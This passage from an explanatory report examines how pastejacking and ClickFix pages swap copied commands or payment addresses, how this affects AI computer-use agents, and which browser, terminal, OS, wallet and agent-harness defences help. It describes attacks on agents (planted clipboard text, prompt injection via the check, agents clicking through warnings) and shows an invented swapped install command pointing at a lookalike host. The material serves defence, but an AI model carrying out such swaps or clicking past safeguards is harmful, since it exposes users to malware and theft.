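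With the label, a terminal could name the source site and wait for confirmation, or insert the text without its line breaks so that nothing runs until someone presses Enter. It could also refuse commands from any site that the user or their employer had not approved. The security zone alone would help little, because the real Homebrew site and its copies are all on the public internet. macOS already uses a related clue, the application the text came from, when someone pastes into Terminal.

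A refusal by the browser would also work for agents, because it doesn't rely on anyone paying attention. A prompt's effectiveness would depend on who answers it. An agent would see the site's name and could compare it with the site it meant to visit, but it might simply confirm.

The label would be most useful against ClickFix pages and cloned sites, where the address itself is wrong. Lawrence describes it for text that a user copies from the web, and to catch planted text, browsers would also have to attach it when a script does the writing. It can't reveal a swap by the site that the agent intended to use:

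| Page | Command displayed | Command pasted | Source label |
|---|---|---|---|
| Genuine site | Genuine | Genuine | Genuine site |
| Cloned site | Genuine | Malicious | Cloned site |
| Genuine site after a break-in | Genuine | Malicious | Genuine site |

The label is the same in the top and bottom rows because it records which page the text came from, not what the page displayed. Similarly, if attackers changed the Copy button on a supplier's invoice page to copy a false payment address, the label on that address would correctly name the supplier.

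A browser can detect whether copied text came from the user's selection or from a script, and could add that to the label. A terminal could then be stricter with text from a script. But text from legitimate Copy buttons and web-based editors would also be labeled as coming from a script, and hidden text within the selection would still count as the user's selection.

Labels can also get lost. When mac-use-mcp restores planted text to the clipboard after typing, the text would come back without its label, because the tool saves only the text. A terminal that trusted unlabelled text would then accept it. In other cases, a missing label could be a useful warning. If an agent copied an address from a browser and the clipboard then held an address with no label, a clipper might have replaced it, though a careful clipper could forge the label. All of this is inferred from how the formats and the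 code work.

Participants in the November 2025 session had related ideas for agents that work inside a browser. One suggested tracking where an agent's information came from, so that a site could refuse information from a particular source. Another suggested limiting which sites an agent may paste data into. The browser could enforce this limit whatever the model decided, but it would not stop an agent from pasting a command into a terminal, which is outside the browser.

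## Warnings and checks at the moment of pasting

If text gets past the browser's rules, a terminal, operating system or wallet may still check it when someone pastes it. Developers built these checks for people, so many depend on the user reading a warning, and some use the user's past behaviour to guess whether they need one.

### Line breaks in terminals

Bracketed paste keeps a line break in pasted text from running a command. The terminal puts invisible markers before and after the pasted text so that the shell, the program that interprets typed commands, can tell pasted characters from typed ones. The shell then treats the line break as ordinary text and waits for a real press of Enter. cirw.in's *bracketed paste mode* recommends the feature to people who paste carelessly, because it gives them time to check what they pasted.

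Bracketed paste was originally designed for purposes other than security. Dickey (2022), who maintains the terminal program xterm, dates the first version to 2002. It became better known after 2005, when a text editor's developer wanted to stop his program from indenting pasted code twice. Shells adopted it much later. Zsh, now the default on Macs, added it in 2015. Ramey (2021), in *In which version was enable-bracketed-paste introduced?*, confirms that Bash, the usual shell on Linux, has supported it since version 4.4 and turned it on by default in version 5.1.

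The markers work only if both the terminal and the program running in it support them. PuTTY, a terminal program, sends pasted text exactly as if the user had typed it unless the program running in it asks for markers, according to *4.6.12 Disabling bracketed paste mode* in WA2L/WinTools' copy of the PuTTY manual. This suggests that an agent connected to an old server could still run a command just by pasting it.

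Dickey calls bracketed paste "nothing more than a clue" about where input came from. It marks the end of pasted text with a string of characters, so an attacker can include that string in the text to make the rest look typed. Terminals try to remove such markers, but the filter in the kitty terminal had a gap until June 2018. Dickey advises against pasting into a shell from any unfiltered source. He also added settings to xterm that strip control characters from pastes.

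Bracketed paste should help agents as much as people, because it works whether or not anyone notices an attack. The swapped command stays at the prompt without running, and the next screenshot will show it. This doesn't help if the agent sends Enter in the same batch as the paste.

Harnesses can also interfere with bracketed paste. If a harness read the clipboard and sent the contents as keystrokes, the terminal would not mark them as a paste, and a line break would run the command. If a harness types by pasting, as ui-tars does, a line break that the model meant as Enter would not submit anything. Both points are inferences from how the markers work.

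### Prompts before a paste

Some terminals require confirmation before accepting certain pastes. Microsoft's *Interaction settings in Windows Terminal* describes one warning dialog for text with several lines and another for text over 5 KiB, both on by default. Microsoft recommends the multi-line warning for people who copy commands from untrusted websites, since each line may run before they have read it.

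Windows Terminal also trims trailing whitespace from pasted text by default. If this includes line breaks, a single command that ends with a line break would presumably be pasted without it and wait for Enter, and no dialog would appear.

The terminal rxvt-unicode has an optional prompt that ManKier's *urxvt-confirm-paste* describes as a defence against browsers that paste different text from what the user selected. When a paste contains control characters, including line breaks, the user can remove them, keep them or cancel the paste. Ghostty, a newer terminal, has a similar check in its code library that classes a command ending in a line break as unsafe.

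These prompts check the form of the text, and a swapped command can have an ordinary form. rxvt-unicode's *urxvt-confirm-paste* (2026) states that text without control characters is pasted without a prompt. An attacker can therefore avoid the prompt by putting everything on one line, and the command runs when the agent presses Enter.

The smaller project ttyx_ checks the commands themselves. Its *Security features* describes a preview in which the user can read, edit or cancel a multi-line paste before any of it reaches the shell. The program gives a stronger warning every time the text matches a dangerous pattern, such as a mass deletion or a download piped into a shell. An agent that takes a screenshot of the preview can compare the text with the web page before pasting. Like Opera's filter, the warning alone wouldn't distinguish the two commands.

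Batching can defeat the prompts too. If an agent sends a paste and Enter together, the dialog opens after the paste and receives the Enter. If Enter activates the confirm button, the agent approves a warning that was never shown to the model. If it activates Cancel, both the attack and the agent's task fail. Terminal developers could therefore make Cancel the default. This analysis is an inference from the order of events.

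### Apple's alert for people who rarely use Terminal

Apple added two kinds of paste alert to macOS 26.4, released on 24 March 2026. One has the heading "Possible malware, Paste blocked" and a Paste Anyway button. Apple's *If your Mac blocks a Terminal command paste or script* explains that people see it if they don't regularly use Terminal and copied the command from somewhere like a website, a chat agent or an email app.

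Apple's *Terminal and script protections* gives the exact conditions, all of which must hold:

- The user hasn't opened Terminal for more than 30 days.
- The Mac has no common developer tools on it, such as Xcode.
- The text comes from one of a set list of apps, including popular browsers, Mail and Messages.

A new Mac also has a grace period of 24 hours after setup, during which the alert doesn't appear.

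To decide whether to show its paste alert, macOS Terminal checks whether the app that put the text on the clipboard is on a list of 74 apps. The text itself makes no difference. In *macOS 26.4 Paste Protection* (2026), a collection of early findings, Adam Codega reports that even "hello world" can set off the alert.

These conditions confused people at first. AppleInsider (2026) couldn't make the alert appear and wondered whether the first screenshot was a hoax. The blogger Dr. Drang used Safari to copy a command that would download a script and immediately run it. When he pasted the command into Terminal and pressed Return, the script deleted his test folder without any warning from macOS. He writes about his usual way of working in Terminal, so he probably used it too regularly to see the alert.

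Judging from Apple's conditions, the alert seems to have several weaknesses when an agent is pasting. The agent may click Paste Anyway because the user has asked it to install something. The alert also looks the same whether the command is genuine or swapped, so it gives the model no new evidence about this particular command. The wording about scammers might still persuade a cautious model to stop and ask the user.

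More often, the alert may not appear at all. Apple treats recent use of Terminal as a sign of experience, and opening Terminal resets the 30-day count, so an agent that uses it every week keeps the alert off. On a shared Mac, the alert also stays off for the owner, who may never have opened Terminal and could fall for a ClickFix page with no warning.

Developer tools also prevent the alert, and a Mac set up for coding agents will usually have them. The grace period prevents it too if the agent works in a virtual machine that its operator creates for each job and deletes the same day.

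AppleInsider relays a user's report that the alert appears only once. The testing instructions quoted in *macOS 26.4 Paste Protection* are consistent with this, since they include deleting a stored record that the user has acknowledged the warning. If an agent clicked Paste Anyway while installing a legitimate program, the owner might not see the alert on a later, malicious paste.

A harness that restores planted text to the clipboard, as mac-use-mcp does, could also prevent the alert, because macOS would presumably record the harness rather than the browser as the text's source.

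### Apple's block on known malware

The other alert has the heading "Malware Detected, Paste Blocked". It works in any terminal program, regardless of how often the person uses one. Apple says that XProtect, the Mac's built-in malware scanner, follows the processes that a pasted command starts. It checks the web addresses involved against a list of known malicious ones, looks for behaviour typical of malware and can stop the process. Some of this checking therefore happens after the command has started, despite the heading.

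MacRumors' *Apple Details Terminal Anti-Scam Warning in macOS* (2026) notes that this alert has no Paste Anyway button. Without one, an agent can't choose to continue, and a batched press of Enter can't approve the command. A user who thinks the block is a mistake can report the blocked website to Apple.

Chris (2026), in *ClickFix-Angriff über Reddit*, reports that the block stopped the command behind a fake HBO Max advertisement in the Reddit campaign described earlier. The campaign's commands kept changing, and the report doesn't establish how many of them the block would have stopped.

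In *No Paste for You!*, Wardle (2026) worked out how macOS gets information about a paste. On a test machine, he found that the clipboard service requests authorisation when someone pastes. XProtect receives a record of the text, the app it came from and the app receiving it. Wardle then wrote a small program that received the same records for every paste.

That program worked only because he had turned off some of the Mac's protections. Apple reserves these records for its own software. BlockBlock, Wardle's free security tool, has to watch for the Command+V shortcut instead, an approach he calls "somewhat reactive". An agent that pasted from the Edit menu would presumably get past a tool that watches only for the shortcut.

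Even Apple's record doesn't include the command that the web page displayed. This suggests that a swapped command could get through if it downloads from an address nobody has reported yet, at least until its behaviour shows that it is malicious.

The block also applies only to pastes, so it would miss a command that the model typed or ran through a separate shell tool. Jamf's *ClickFix technique uses Script Editor instead of Terminal on macOS* describes a campaign against human victims in which a web page opens Script Editor, an Apple program for writing and running scripts, instead of Terminal. According to AppleInsider's *Mac Script Editor becomes new entry point for ClickFix malware*, this avoids the scan of pasted commands. macOS 26.4 also scans scripts, but it blocks only those that match known malware.

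### Phones and developer consoles

Phone makers have mostly tried to stop apps from reading the clipboard, which may hold a password or a private message. Since 2020, iPhones have shown a notice when one app reads text copied in another, and since 2022 they have asked for permission if the user didn't choose to paste. Android stopped most background apps from reading the clipboard in 2019 and added a notice in 2021.

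These measures identify the app that is about to receive the text, but pastejacking is carried out by the page that wrote the text to the clipboard. A permission prompt would therefore look the same whether or not the text had been swapped. An agent operating a phone could truthfully confirm that it wanted to paste into its wallet app and still paste the attacker's address.

Since Android 13, released in 2022, Android has shown a small preview of newly copied text, which could incidentally help agents catch pastejacking. An agent that pressed a Copy button and then took a screenshot might see the swapped text before pasting it. This is an inference, and a long command or address might not fit in the preview.

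Browsers protect their developer consoles more strictly. A console runs code inside the page the user has open, so a scammer who gets someone to paste code there can take over their account on that site. text/plain reports that Chromium and Firefox now block pasting into the console by default. The user lifts the block by typing a short phrase that the browser displays, which an agent can do as easily as clicking a button. Firefox also stops asking for the phrase once a few commands have been run in the console, so an agent that runs commands there could remove the protection for its user as well.

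Browsers treat their address bars in a similar way. If someone pastes script there, the browser removes the prefix that would make it run, and the user has to type the prefix by hand. This adds a step but doesn't prevent the attack, as the campaign against cryptocurrency traders showed. An agent can type the prefix without effort, so any remaining protection depends on whether the model checks why the prefix is needed.

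### Payment addresses

A wallet usually checks whether a pasted address has a valid checksum. Ethereum encodes the checksum in the address's capitalisation, using a standard formula to determine from the 40 hexadecimal digits which letters to capitalise. If someone mistypes a digit, the capitals will almost certainly not match the formula. Many wallets also accept all-lowercase addresses, which carry no checksum.

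The attacker's address also passes the checksum test, because the formula doesn't check who should receive the money. Checksums in bank account numbers have the same limitation, though a bank can also compare the account holder's name with the one the payer entered. An ordinary cryptocurrency address has no registered name to compare.

That leaves comparing the address with the intended one, and wallets encourage people to look only at the ends by shortening addresses to their first and last few characters. The attacker's work grows quickly with the number of digits compared. The times below assume a machine that tests 100 million addresses a second:

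| Digits compared | Average attempts | Time |
|---|---|---|
| 4 | 65,536 | Under a thousandth of a second |
| 8 | 4.3 billion | 43 seconds |
| 12 | 281 trillion | 33 days |
| 16 | 18 quintillion | About 5,800 years |

An attacker therefore needs less than a minute of computing to match four digits at each end, and can do it before the victim arrives. Checking twelve digits in total would deter a casual thief, but one with a thousand such machines could match them in about 47 minutes.

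Checking digits that the attacker couldn't predict works better. If the attacker has matched both ends and the victim compares four digits somewhere in the middle, the chance that all four match is 1 in 65,536. A program can compare all 40 digits just as easily, so an agent's developer has no reason to check fewer.

Another option is to restrict where the money can go. Some cryptocurrency exchanges let customers limit withdrawals to addresses they have already saved, and some make customers wait before using a newly added address. A withdrawal to a swapped address would then fail even if nobody compared the addresses, unless the agent had saved the swapped one as a new recipient. The saved address must itself be correct, so the customer should add it without using the agent's clipboard.

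### Confirming on a hardware wallet

A hardware wallet is a small device that stores the secret keys needed to spend cryptocurrency. The computer prepares a payment and sends it to the device, which shows the amount and the recipient's address on its own screen. The owner then presses a button to approve the payment. Malware on the computer can change what the monitor shows but normally can't change the device's display.

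The owner needs to compare the address on the device's screen with the one the supplier gave them, for example by phone or for an earlier payment. In a pastejacking attack, the false address enters the wallet program before it reaches the device, so both show it. An owner who compares only those two will see that they match and approve the payment to the attacker.

An agent usually can't do this step because it can't see the device's screen or press its button. A person has to do it, so the device prevents the agent from sending the money on its own.

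But the person may not have seen the invoice. If they ask the agent which address to expect, and the agent reads it from the wallet program, they will again compare the attacker's address with itself. The agent would need to quote the address from the invoice page, and even that wouldn't help if the attackers had also changed the address shown there. These are inferences from how the device works, not reported failures.

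### How people and agents respond to warnings

Warnings stop many people, though how many depends on the design. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analysed more than 25 million warnings shown in Chrome and Firefox. Users clicked past fewer than a quarter of malware and phishing warnings in either browser. For warnings about faulty security certificates, which often appear on harmless sites, the figure was 70.2% in Chrome and 33.0% in Firefox.

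A warning's effect also depends on whether it interrupts the user. Egelman, Cranor and Hong (2008), in *You've Been Warned*, sent simulated phishing emails to 60 people. When a warning blocked the page until they made a choice, 79% of those who saw it heeded it. Only one participant heeded a warning that didn't block the page. Apple's alerts and the terminal dialogs interrupt the user, while the notices on phones mostly don't.

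Warnings become less effective when people see them repeatedly. In *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain*, Anderson and colleagues (2015) scanned people's brains and found that visual processing of a warning dropped sharply by the second time they saw it. This is a good argument for Apple's narrow conditions, because people would soon start dismissing a warning that appeared on every paste.

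No published study seems to have tested how agents respond to genuine paste warnings. The nearest evidence concerns hostile pop-ups. *Attacking Vision-Language Computer Agents via Pop-ups* (Zhang, Yu and Yang, 2024) found that agents clicked them 86% of the time on average, and that telling the agents to ignore pop-ups did little to help. The models tested are old, and the pop-ups contained text designed to attract a click, so the figure doesn't predict what a current model would do with Apple's alert.

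Agents may also handle repeated warnings better than people do, because a model doesn't get bored and can read the tenth warning of the day as carefully as the first. But it may have learned during training to close dialog boxes in order to finish tasks. Researchers could easily test which tendency is stronger by showing an agent the same paste warning over genuine and swapped commands and counting how often it cancels each. If it cancels both equally often, it is reacting to the dialog rather than to the command.

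The table sorts the defences by what they rely on. Most of the last column is inference.

| Defence | What triggers it | When an agent pastes |
|---|---|---|
| **Automatic blocks** | | |
| Bracketed paste | Any paste, if the terminal and shell support it | Holds the command until the agent presses Enter |
| macOS block on known malware | A pasted command linked to known malware or behaving like it | Works without the agent's judgement, but can miss new malware |
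| Address checksum | A mistyped or damaged address | Accepts the attacker's valid address |
| Withdrawals limited to saved addresses | A payment to any other address | Blocks the payment unless the agent can add addresses |
| **Questions that need a person** | | |
| Multi-line and control-character prompts | Line breaks or other control characters | The agent may confirm, and a one-line command gets no prompt |
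| Phone paste permission | An app reading text copied elsewhere | The agent can allow it, and the prompt doesn't reveal a swap |
| Hardware wallet | A request to approve a payment | A person must compare the address with an independent copy |
| **Rules based on a user's habits** | | |
| macOS "Possible malware" alert | A paste from a listed app, with no recent Terminal use or developer tools | The agent may click through, or its own Terminal use may prevent the alert |
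| Developer console block | A paste by someone new to the console | The agent can type the phrase that lifts it |

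## Checks built into the agent

A browser handles only the copy, and a terminal or wallet handles only the paste. An agent's harness carries out both, so it can check whether the pasted text is what the agent meant to copy. Current products mostly take the simpler approach of limiting which programs the agent may operate.

### What Claude's permissions block

In a research preview, Claude Code can operate a Mac desktop. Anthropic's *Let Claude use your computer from the CLI* explains that Claude must ask before using each application in a session. The request also lists any extra permissions, such as clipboard access. Anthropic doesn't specify whether clipboard access means reading the clipboard, writing to it or pasting from it. The user grants the permission for the session, so they don't approve any particular text.

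How much Claude can do in an approved application depends on the application's category. Anthropic lets Claude look at browsers and trading platforms but not click in them. In terminals and code editors, Claude can click and scroll but can't type or use keyboard shortcuts. It has full control of all other approved applications. Users can't change these access levels.

| Step in the attack | Claude Code's rule | What remains possible |
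|---|---|---|
| Copy from the web page | No clicks or keys in browsers | Copying through Claude's separate Chrome extension, or from a web page displayed inside another application |
| Paste into a terminal | No typing or shortcuts in terminals | Perhaps choosing Paste from a menu with the mouse |
| Press Enter | No typing in terminals | A line break in the pasted text, if the terminal has no paste protection |
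| Run the command without a terminal window | Shell commands go through a separate tool | Running whatever the model gives that tool |

The last column is inference. The menu route is narrow, because the Mac's default shell holds a pasted line break until someone presses Enter.

The shell tool matters more than terminal windows, since Anthropic has Claude use it for commands whenever possible. Normally the model reads the command and writes it out again, so a swap on the clipboard has no effect. But a shell can also read the clipboard. If the model used it to fetch and run the copied text in one step, a swapped command would presumably run without the model having read it, and the limits on terminal windows wouldn't apply.

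Anthropic also offers a sandbox that restricts the shell tool's commands to chosen directories and network hosts, as described in its *Beyond permission prompts*. A swapped command couldn't download malware from any other host, but it could still download it from a chosen one, such as a popular code-hosting site where anyone can upload files.

According to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide*, users of the Chrome extension can approve a plan themselves, let an automatic safety check review each action, or skip approvals altogether. Pressing a Copy button is not on the list of actions that always need permission. Purchases and financial transactions are forbidden in every mode, so the extension should refuse to send a payment even if the wrong address is already in the form.

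Cowork is Anthropic's product for general office tasks. *Let Claude use your computer in Cowork* describes Claude clicking and typing in the browser, so the view-only rule may be specific to Claude Code. Cowork blocks cryptocurrency and trading applications by default. Anthropic warns that actions in one application can affect another. For example, a link that Claude clicks in an email may open in Chrome, even if the user never gave Claude access to it. The clipboard can presumably connect applications in the same way, because text copied in an approved application can end up wherever the user next pastes.

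### Rules at OpenAI, Google and Microsoft

OpenAI's coding agent Codex can use a browser and other approved Mac applications, and can access their "clipboard state". It can't operate terminal applications, because doing so could bypass its security policies. It could therefore press a malicious Copy button but not paste the copied text into a terminal window. Separate approval and sandbox settings apply to its shell commands.

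No such block applies to an approved wallet, though OpenAI advises users to stay present for payments. They may not be able to watch, because Codex can use approved applications while the screen is locked, according to MacRumors' *OpenAI's Codex Can Now Use Your Mac Even When It's Locked* (2026). OpenAI now also offers computer use in the ChatGPT desktop app. OpenAI's *Using your computer and browser* describes the app's settings for allowed applications and websites but doesn't repeat the rule about terminals.

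Google sells developers a model and a tool, and lets them decide which programs the agent can reach. It defines seven categories of action, including payments, that the model may block or refer to the user. None specifically covers running commands, although the category for changes to files might cover installing software. Developers can switch some categories off.

A recent Gemini model includes a short statement of purpose with each action. For a paste, the statement would presumably describe the text the model expects, so a user relying on it could approve a swapped command. Under Google's policies, the agent also leaves cookie notices to the user. The page can still plant text, because the user's click lets it write to the clipboard just as the agent's click would.

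Microsoft relies more on isolating agents. According to Microsoft's *Securing AI agents on Windows* (2025), its Copilot Actions feature is off by default and gives agents their own user account and a contained workspace. Microsoft's *Experimental Agentic Features* adds that the workspace runs in a separate Windows session.

Companies that build agents in Copilot Studio can restrict them to a list of websites and desktop applications, according to Microsoft's *Supercharge Your Agents with Computer Use in Copilot Studio*. Such a list would keep an agent away from a cloned installation page, but not from a tampered copy button on an approved site. Copilot Studio can also notify a human reviewer when the model detects potentially malicious instructions, but a page that silently swaps the copied text may not contain any.

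If nobody answers a review request within a time limit, the run stops. Microsoft warns that a reviewer who didn't start the run probably can't see what the agent was doing, and so can't judge the request properly.

### Comparing before pasting

None of these permissions involves checking the copied text against the text on the page. A developer can add that check, because the harness carries out every keypress and can intercept a paste. The procedure has five steps:

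1. Record the string the task requires, before copying anything. The best source is the user's request, then the page's text, then a screenshot.
2. Copy the string and switch to the program that will receive it.
3. Have the harness read the clipboard.
4. Compare the two strings in full, including their lengths.
5. Paste if they match. If they don't, stop before the committing action and tell the user.

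The model needs to record the text it expects before it sees the clipboard's contents. Otherwise it might record those contents, and the harness would compare the attacker's text with itself. Switching programs before reading the clipboard also helps, because a page normally loses clipboard access when it loses focus. A page that kept its access could leave the correct text in place for the check and replace it a moment later.

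Suppose the page displays an invented command and its Copy button stores another:

```
Recorded:   getapp install notes --from repo.example
Clipboard:  getapp install notes --from rep0.example
```

Both strings have 40 characters. They differ at the 32nd, where a zero replaces the letter "o", so the harness blocks the paste. If the page had added a second command at the end, the lengths would have differed as well.

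The same check works for a 42-character payment address, also invented:

```
Recorded:   0x1111aaaa2222bbbb3333cccc4444dddd5555eeee
Clipboard:  0x11112b7d90c4e6a158f30d9bc27e416ab8f5eeee
```

The first four and last four digits match, so checking only the ends would miss the swap. A full comparison finds the first mismatch at the seventh character.

The harness should treat a mismatch as a failed action and skip the rest of the batch, including any press of Enter or click on Send. With planted text, the user's task doesn't call for any particular string and step 1 leaves nothing to compare, so the harness should refuse to paste.

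If the agent already has the right string, it could type it instead of pasting, which is often better when the string comes from the user's request or the page's text. Copying helps when the agent has read the string from a screenshot, because the clipboard provides a second version that doesn't depend on reading the image correctly. If the two versions match, a misreading and a swap are both unlikely. A mismatch can also warn the user that the page is hostile, which they wouldn't learn if the agent just typed the command.

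The open-source tool clawdcursor enters text by pasting. Its changelog, reproduced by Glama, describes a Windows bug in which writing to the clipboard could fail silently, so the tool pasted whatever the user had copied earlier. Since version 1.5.19, it has checked the clipboard before every paste and typed the text key by key if the clipboard held the wrong string. The bug shows that old clipboard contents can reach a program by accident, and planted text might reach one the same way, without any instructions.

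clawdcursor compares the clipboard with text the model supplied for typing, not with text on a web page. Its documentation gives no figures for how often the check catches an error or raises a false alarm.

### False alarms

Strict comparison will sometimes block a legitimate transfer. Installation guides often put a prompt symbol such as "$" in front of a command to show that it belongs in a terminal. The model may record the symbol while the Copy button leaves it out. The harness can remove a known prompt from the start of a line before comparing, but it shouldn't remove "#". Some guides use "#" as a prompt, but it also marks a comment, and removing it could turn a harmless comment into a command that runs.

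Line breaks cause a similar problem. A long command may wrap on the screen, so the model may record a line break that isn't in the text. A line break at the end of the clipboard text can be dangerous in an unprotected terminal, so the harness should remove it and paste the cleaned string. In general, the harness should paste exactly the string it compared, not the original clipboard contents.

Some sites append an attribution or a link to anything a visitor copies. The harness shouldn't ignore this extra text, because an attacker could append a command in the same place. It can discard the clipboard's version and type the recorded string instead, provided that string came from the user or the page's text.

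Misread screenshots are harder to fix. Assume that the model gets 0.1% of characters wrong, independently of each other. The chance of at least one error in a 42-character address is:

1 − 0.999⁴² ≈ 0.041

About 4% of addresses in honest payments would therefore raise a false alarm, compared with 18% of 200-character commands. The error rate is assumed, and the true rate will depend on the model and the size of the text.

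Screenshots often lose detail before they reach the model. Claude Code shrinks a 3456×2234 image from a MacBook Pro to about 1372×887, so a letter 20 pixels tall shrinks to about 8. Anthropic advises users to enlarge small text in the application. Developers who build their own harness can use the zoom action instead.

The address's checksum can help distinguish a misreading from a swap. If the recorded Ethereum address uses mixed capitals and fails its checksum, the model has probably misread it and should read it again. If the recorded and copied addresses both pass but differ, a misreading is very unlikely and the harness should stop. Once the checksum has passed, the harness can ignore capitalisation when comparing addresses, because it doesn't affect where the money goes. Commands still need a case-sensitive comparison, because a change of case may select a different file or option.

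A stop doesn't have to end the task. The agent can zoom in, record the string again and repeat the comparison once. After a second mismatch, it should ask the user instead of retrying until its reading happens to match the clipboard.

### Why ordinary code should compare the strings

Giving the model the clipboard's contents and asking whether they look right creates a risk of prompt injection. An attacker who chose that text could include an instruction to the model, such as an explanation of why the difference doesn't matter. The injection could then reach the model through the check meant to catch the swap, even if the page displayed nothing suspicious.

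The harness can avoid this by comparing the strings in ordinary code and returning only "match" or "no match", perhaps with the position of the first difference. The code doesn't interpret the strings, so instructions in the text have no effect. It won't skip a digit in the middle of a long address, or accept an unfamiliar download site because it looks like a plausible mirror.

This protects only the comparison. The model will still read whatever the attacker wrote if it later pastes the text into a document to inspect it, or takes a screenshot after a bad paste. The user may need to see the rejected text to understand what happened, so the harness can show it to them without adding it to the model's conversation.

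### What the alternatives cost

The simplest alternative is to avoid the clipboard. clawdcursor can read a page's exact text through the operating system's accessibility interface, and the harness can then type it. This prevents the clipboard swap and most misreadings. Some applications expose little text through that interface, so the agent must fall back on screenshots for those. Typing a long string is also slower than pasting it.

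Taking another screenshot between the paste and the committing action is almost as simple. Anthropic estimates that each screenshot uses roughly 1,000 to 1,800 input tokens, the units developers pay for when they send text and images. At the speed Claude Opus 4.6 showed in the timing study, ten checked pastes would add about a minute to a task. The check works only if the model detects that the pasted text differs from the copied text, and it comes too late if the paste itself runs the command.

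Tracking where content came from as it moves between programs could cover more attacks. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* proposes that a browser agent keep a list of every site whose content has entered its conversation. The agent could send requests anywhere if the list were empty and only to the listed site if there were one. It could send no requests if there were two or more, because nobody could tell which site had influenced it.

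Trail of Bits, a security firm, designed the rule to prevent data theft. If it were applied strictly to software installation, it would block a lot of ordinary work, since an agent might read a guide on one site and download the program from another. Like a browser's source label, it would also fail to catch text swapped by the site the agent meant to use.

In Choi and colleagues' experiment, which didn't involve the clipboard, strict tracking stopped every data attack but more than halved the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed.

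A harness could track only the clipboard, with less overhead. macOS and Windows both keep a counter that increases whenever the clipboard changes. If the counter goes up after the agent dismisses a cookie notice, something has written to the clipboard without the agent trying to copy, and the harness could block pasting until the agent makes a deliberate copy. This is a proposal based on how the counters work, and the user or another program could trigger a false alarm.

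Human approval can work if the person sees the text that will be pasted. *AgentClick* (Zhuang, Xing and Zhang, 2026) describes a review screen for agents that work in a terminal. The agent submits a proposed command and waits, and the user can read, edit or reject it. A similar screen for pastes would have to take its text from the clipboard. If the model supplied the text, it would submit the command it had read on the page, and the user would approve that command while the harness pasted a different one (an inference).

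Zhuang and colleagues demonstrated the system by revising a plan and editing two emails, one of them from a phone. They describe these as illustrations and didn't run a controlled user study, so there is no figure for how many bad commands reviewers would catch. The agent also takes part by following written instructions, which a model can skip, so a dependable paste check would have to be part of the harness.

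People may also approve without reading. Trail of Bits recommends showing users the exact text that goes to the model, but warns that they are unlikely to study long documents and that reviews can become "security theater". In the *RedTeamCUA* experiments, attacks on OpenAI's Operator succeeded about four times as often when a simulated user approved everything. A screen that shows both the recorded string and the clipboard, with the differences marked, would be easier to check than a single 42-character address. The agent could show it only when the strings differ, so users would rarely see it.

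Isolating the agent limits the damage from a swap but doesn't prevent it. Anthropic and Google both provide sample setups that run the agent in a container, a closed-off environment on the same computer. Malware from a swapped command would reach only the files and passwords inside the container. A payment to the wrong address would still go through, because it happens on the payment network, outside the container.

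A separate clipboard would also stop an agent from leaving a phishing link for its user to paste, as happened in the Atlas demonstration. Windows normally gives each session its own clipboard, so Microsoft's agent workspace may provide this protection, though that is an inference. Virtual machines often share a clipboard with the host computer for convenience, and an operator who wants the protection has to turn sharing off. The user and the agent can then no longer pass text to each other by copying and pasting.

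### What a match proves

If the recorded string came from the page, a match proves only that the page displayed the same text it put on the clipboard. The cloned installation pages that Push Security found would pass this check because the malicious command was visible. The fake addresses in the cryptocurrency campaign that Talos tracked would also pass, because a script changed both the display and the clipboard.

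The harness can catch those only if the recorded string comes from somewhere the attacker doesn't control. For a payment, that means an independent copy of the address, like the one a hardware wallet's owner needs. For an installation, the user could name the official site in the request, or their company could keep a list of approved commands. The harness can then make the same comparison without the agent having to trust the page it found.
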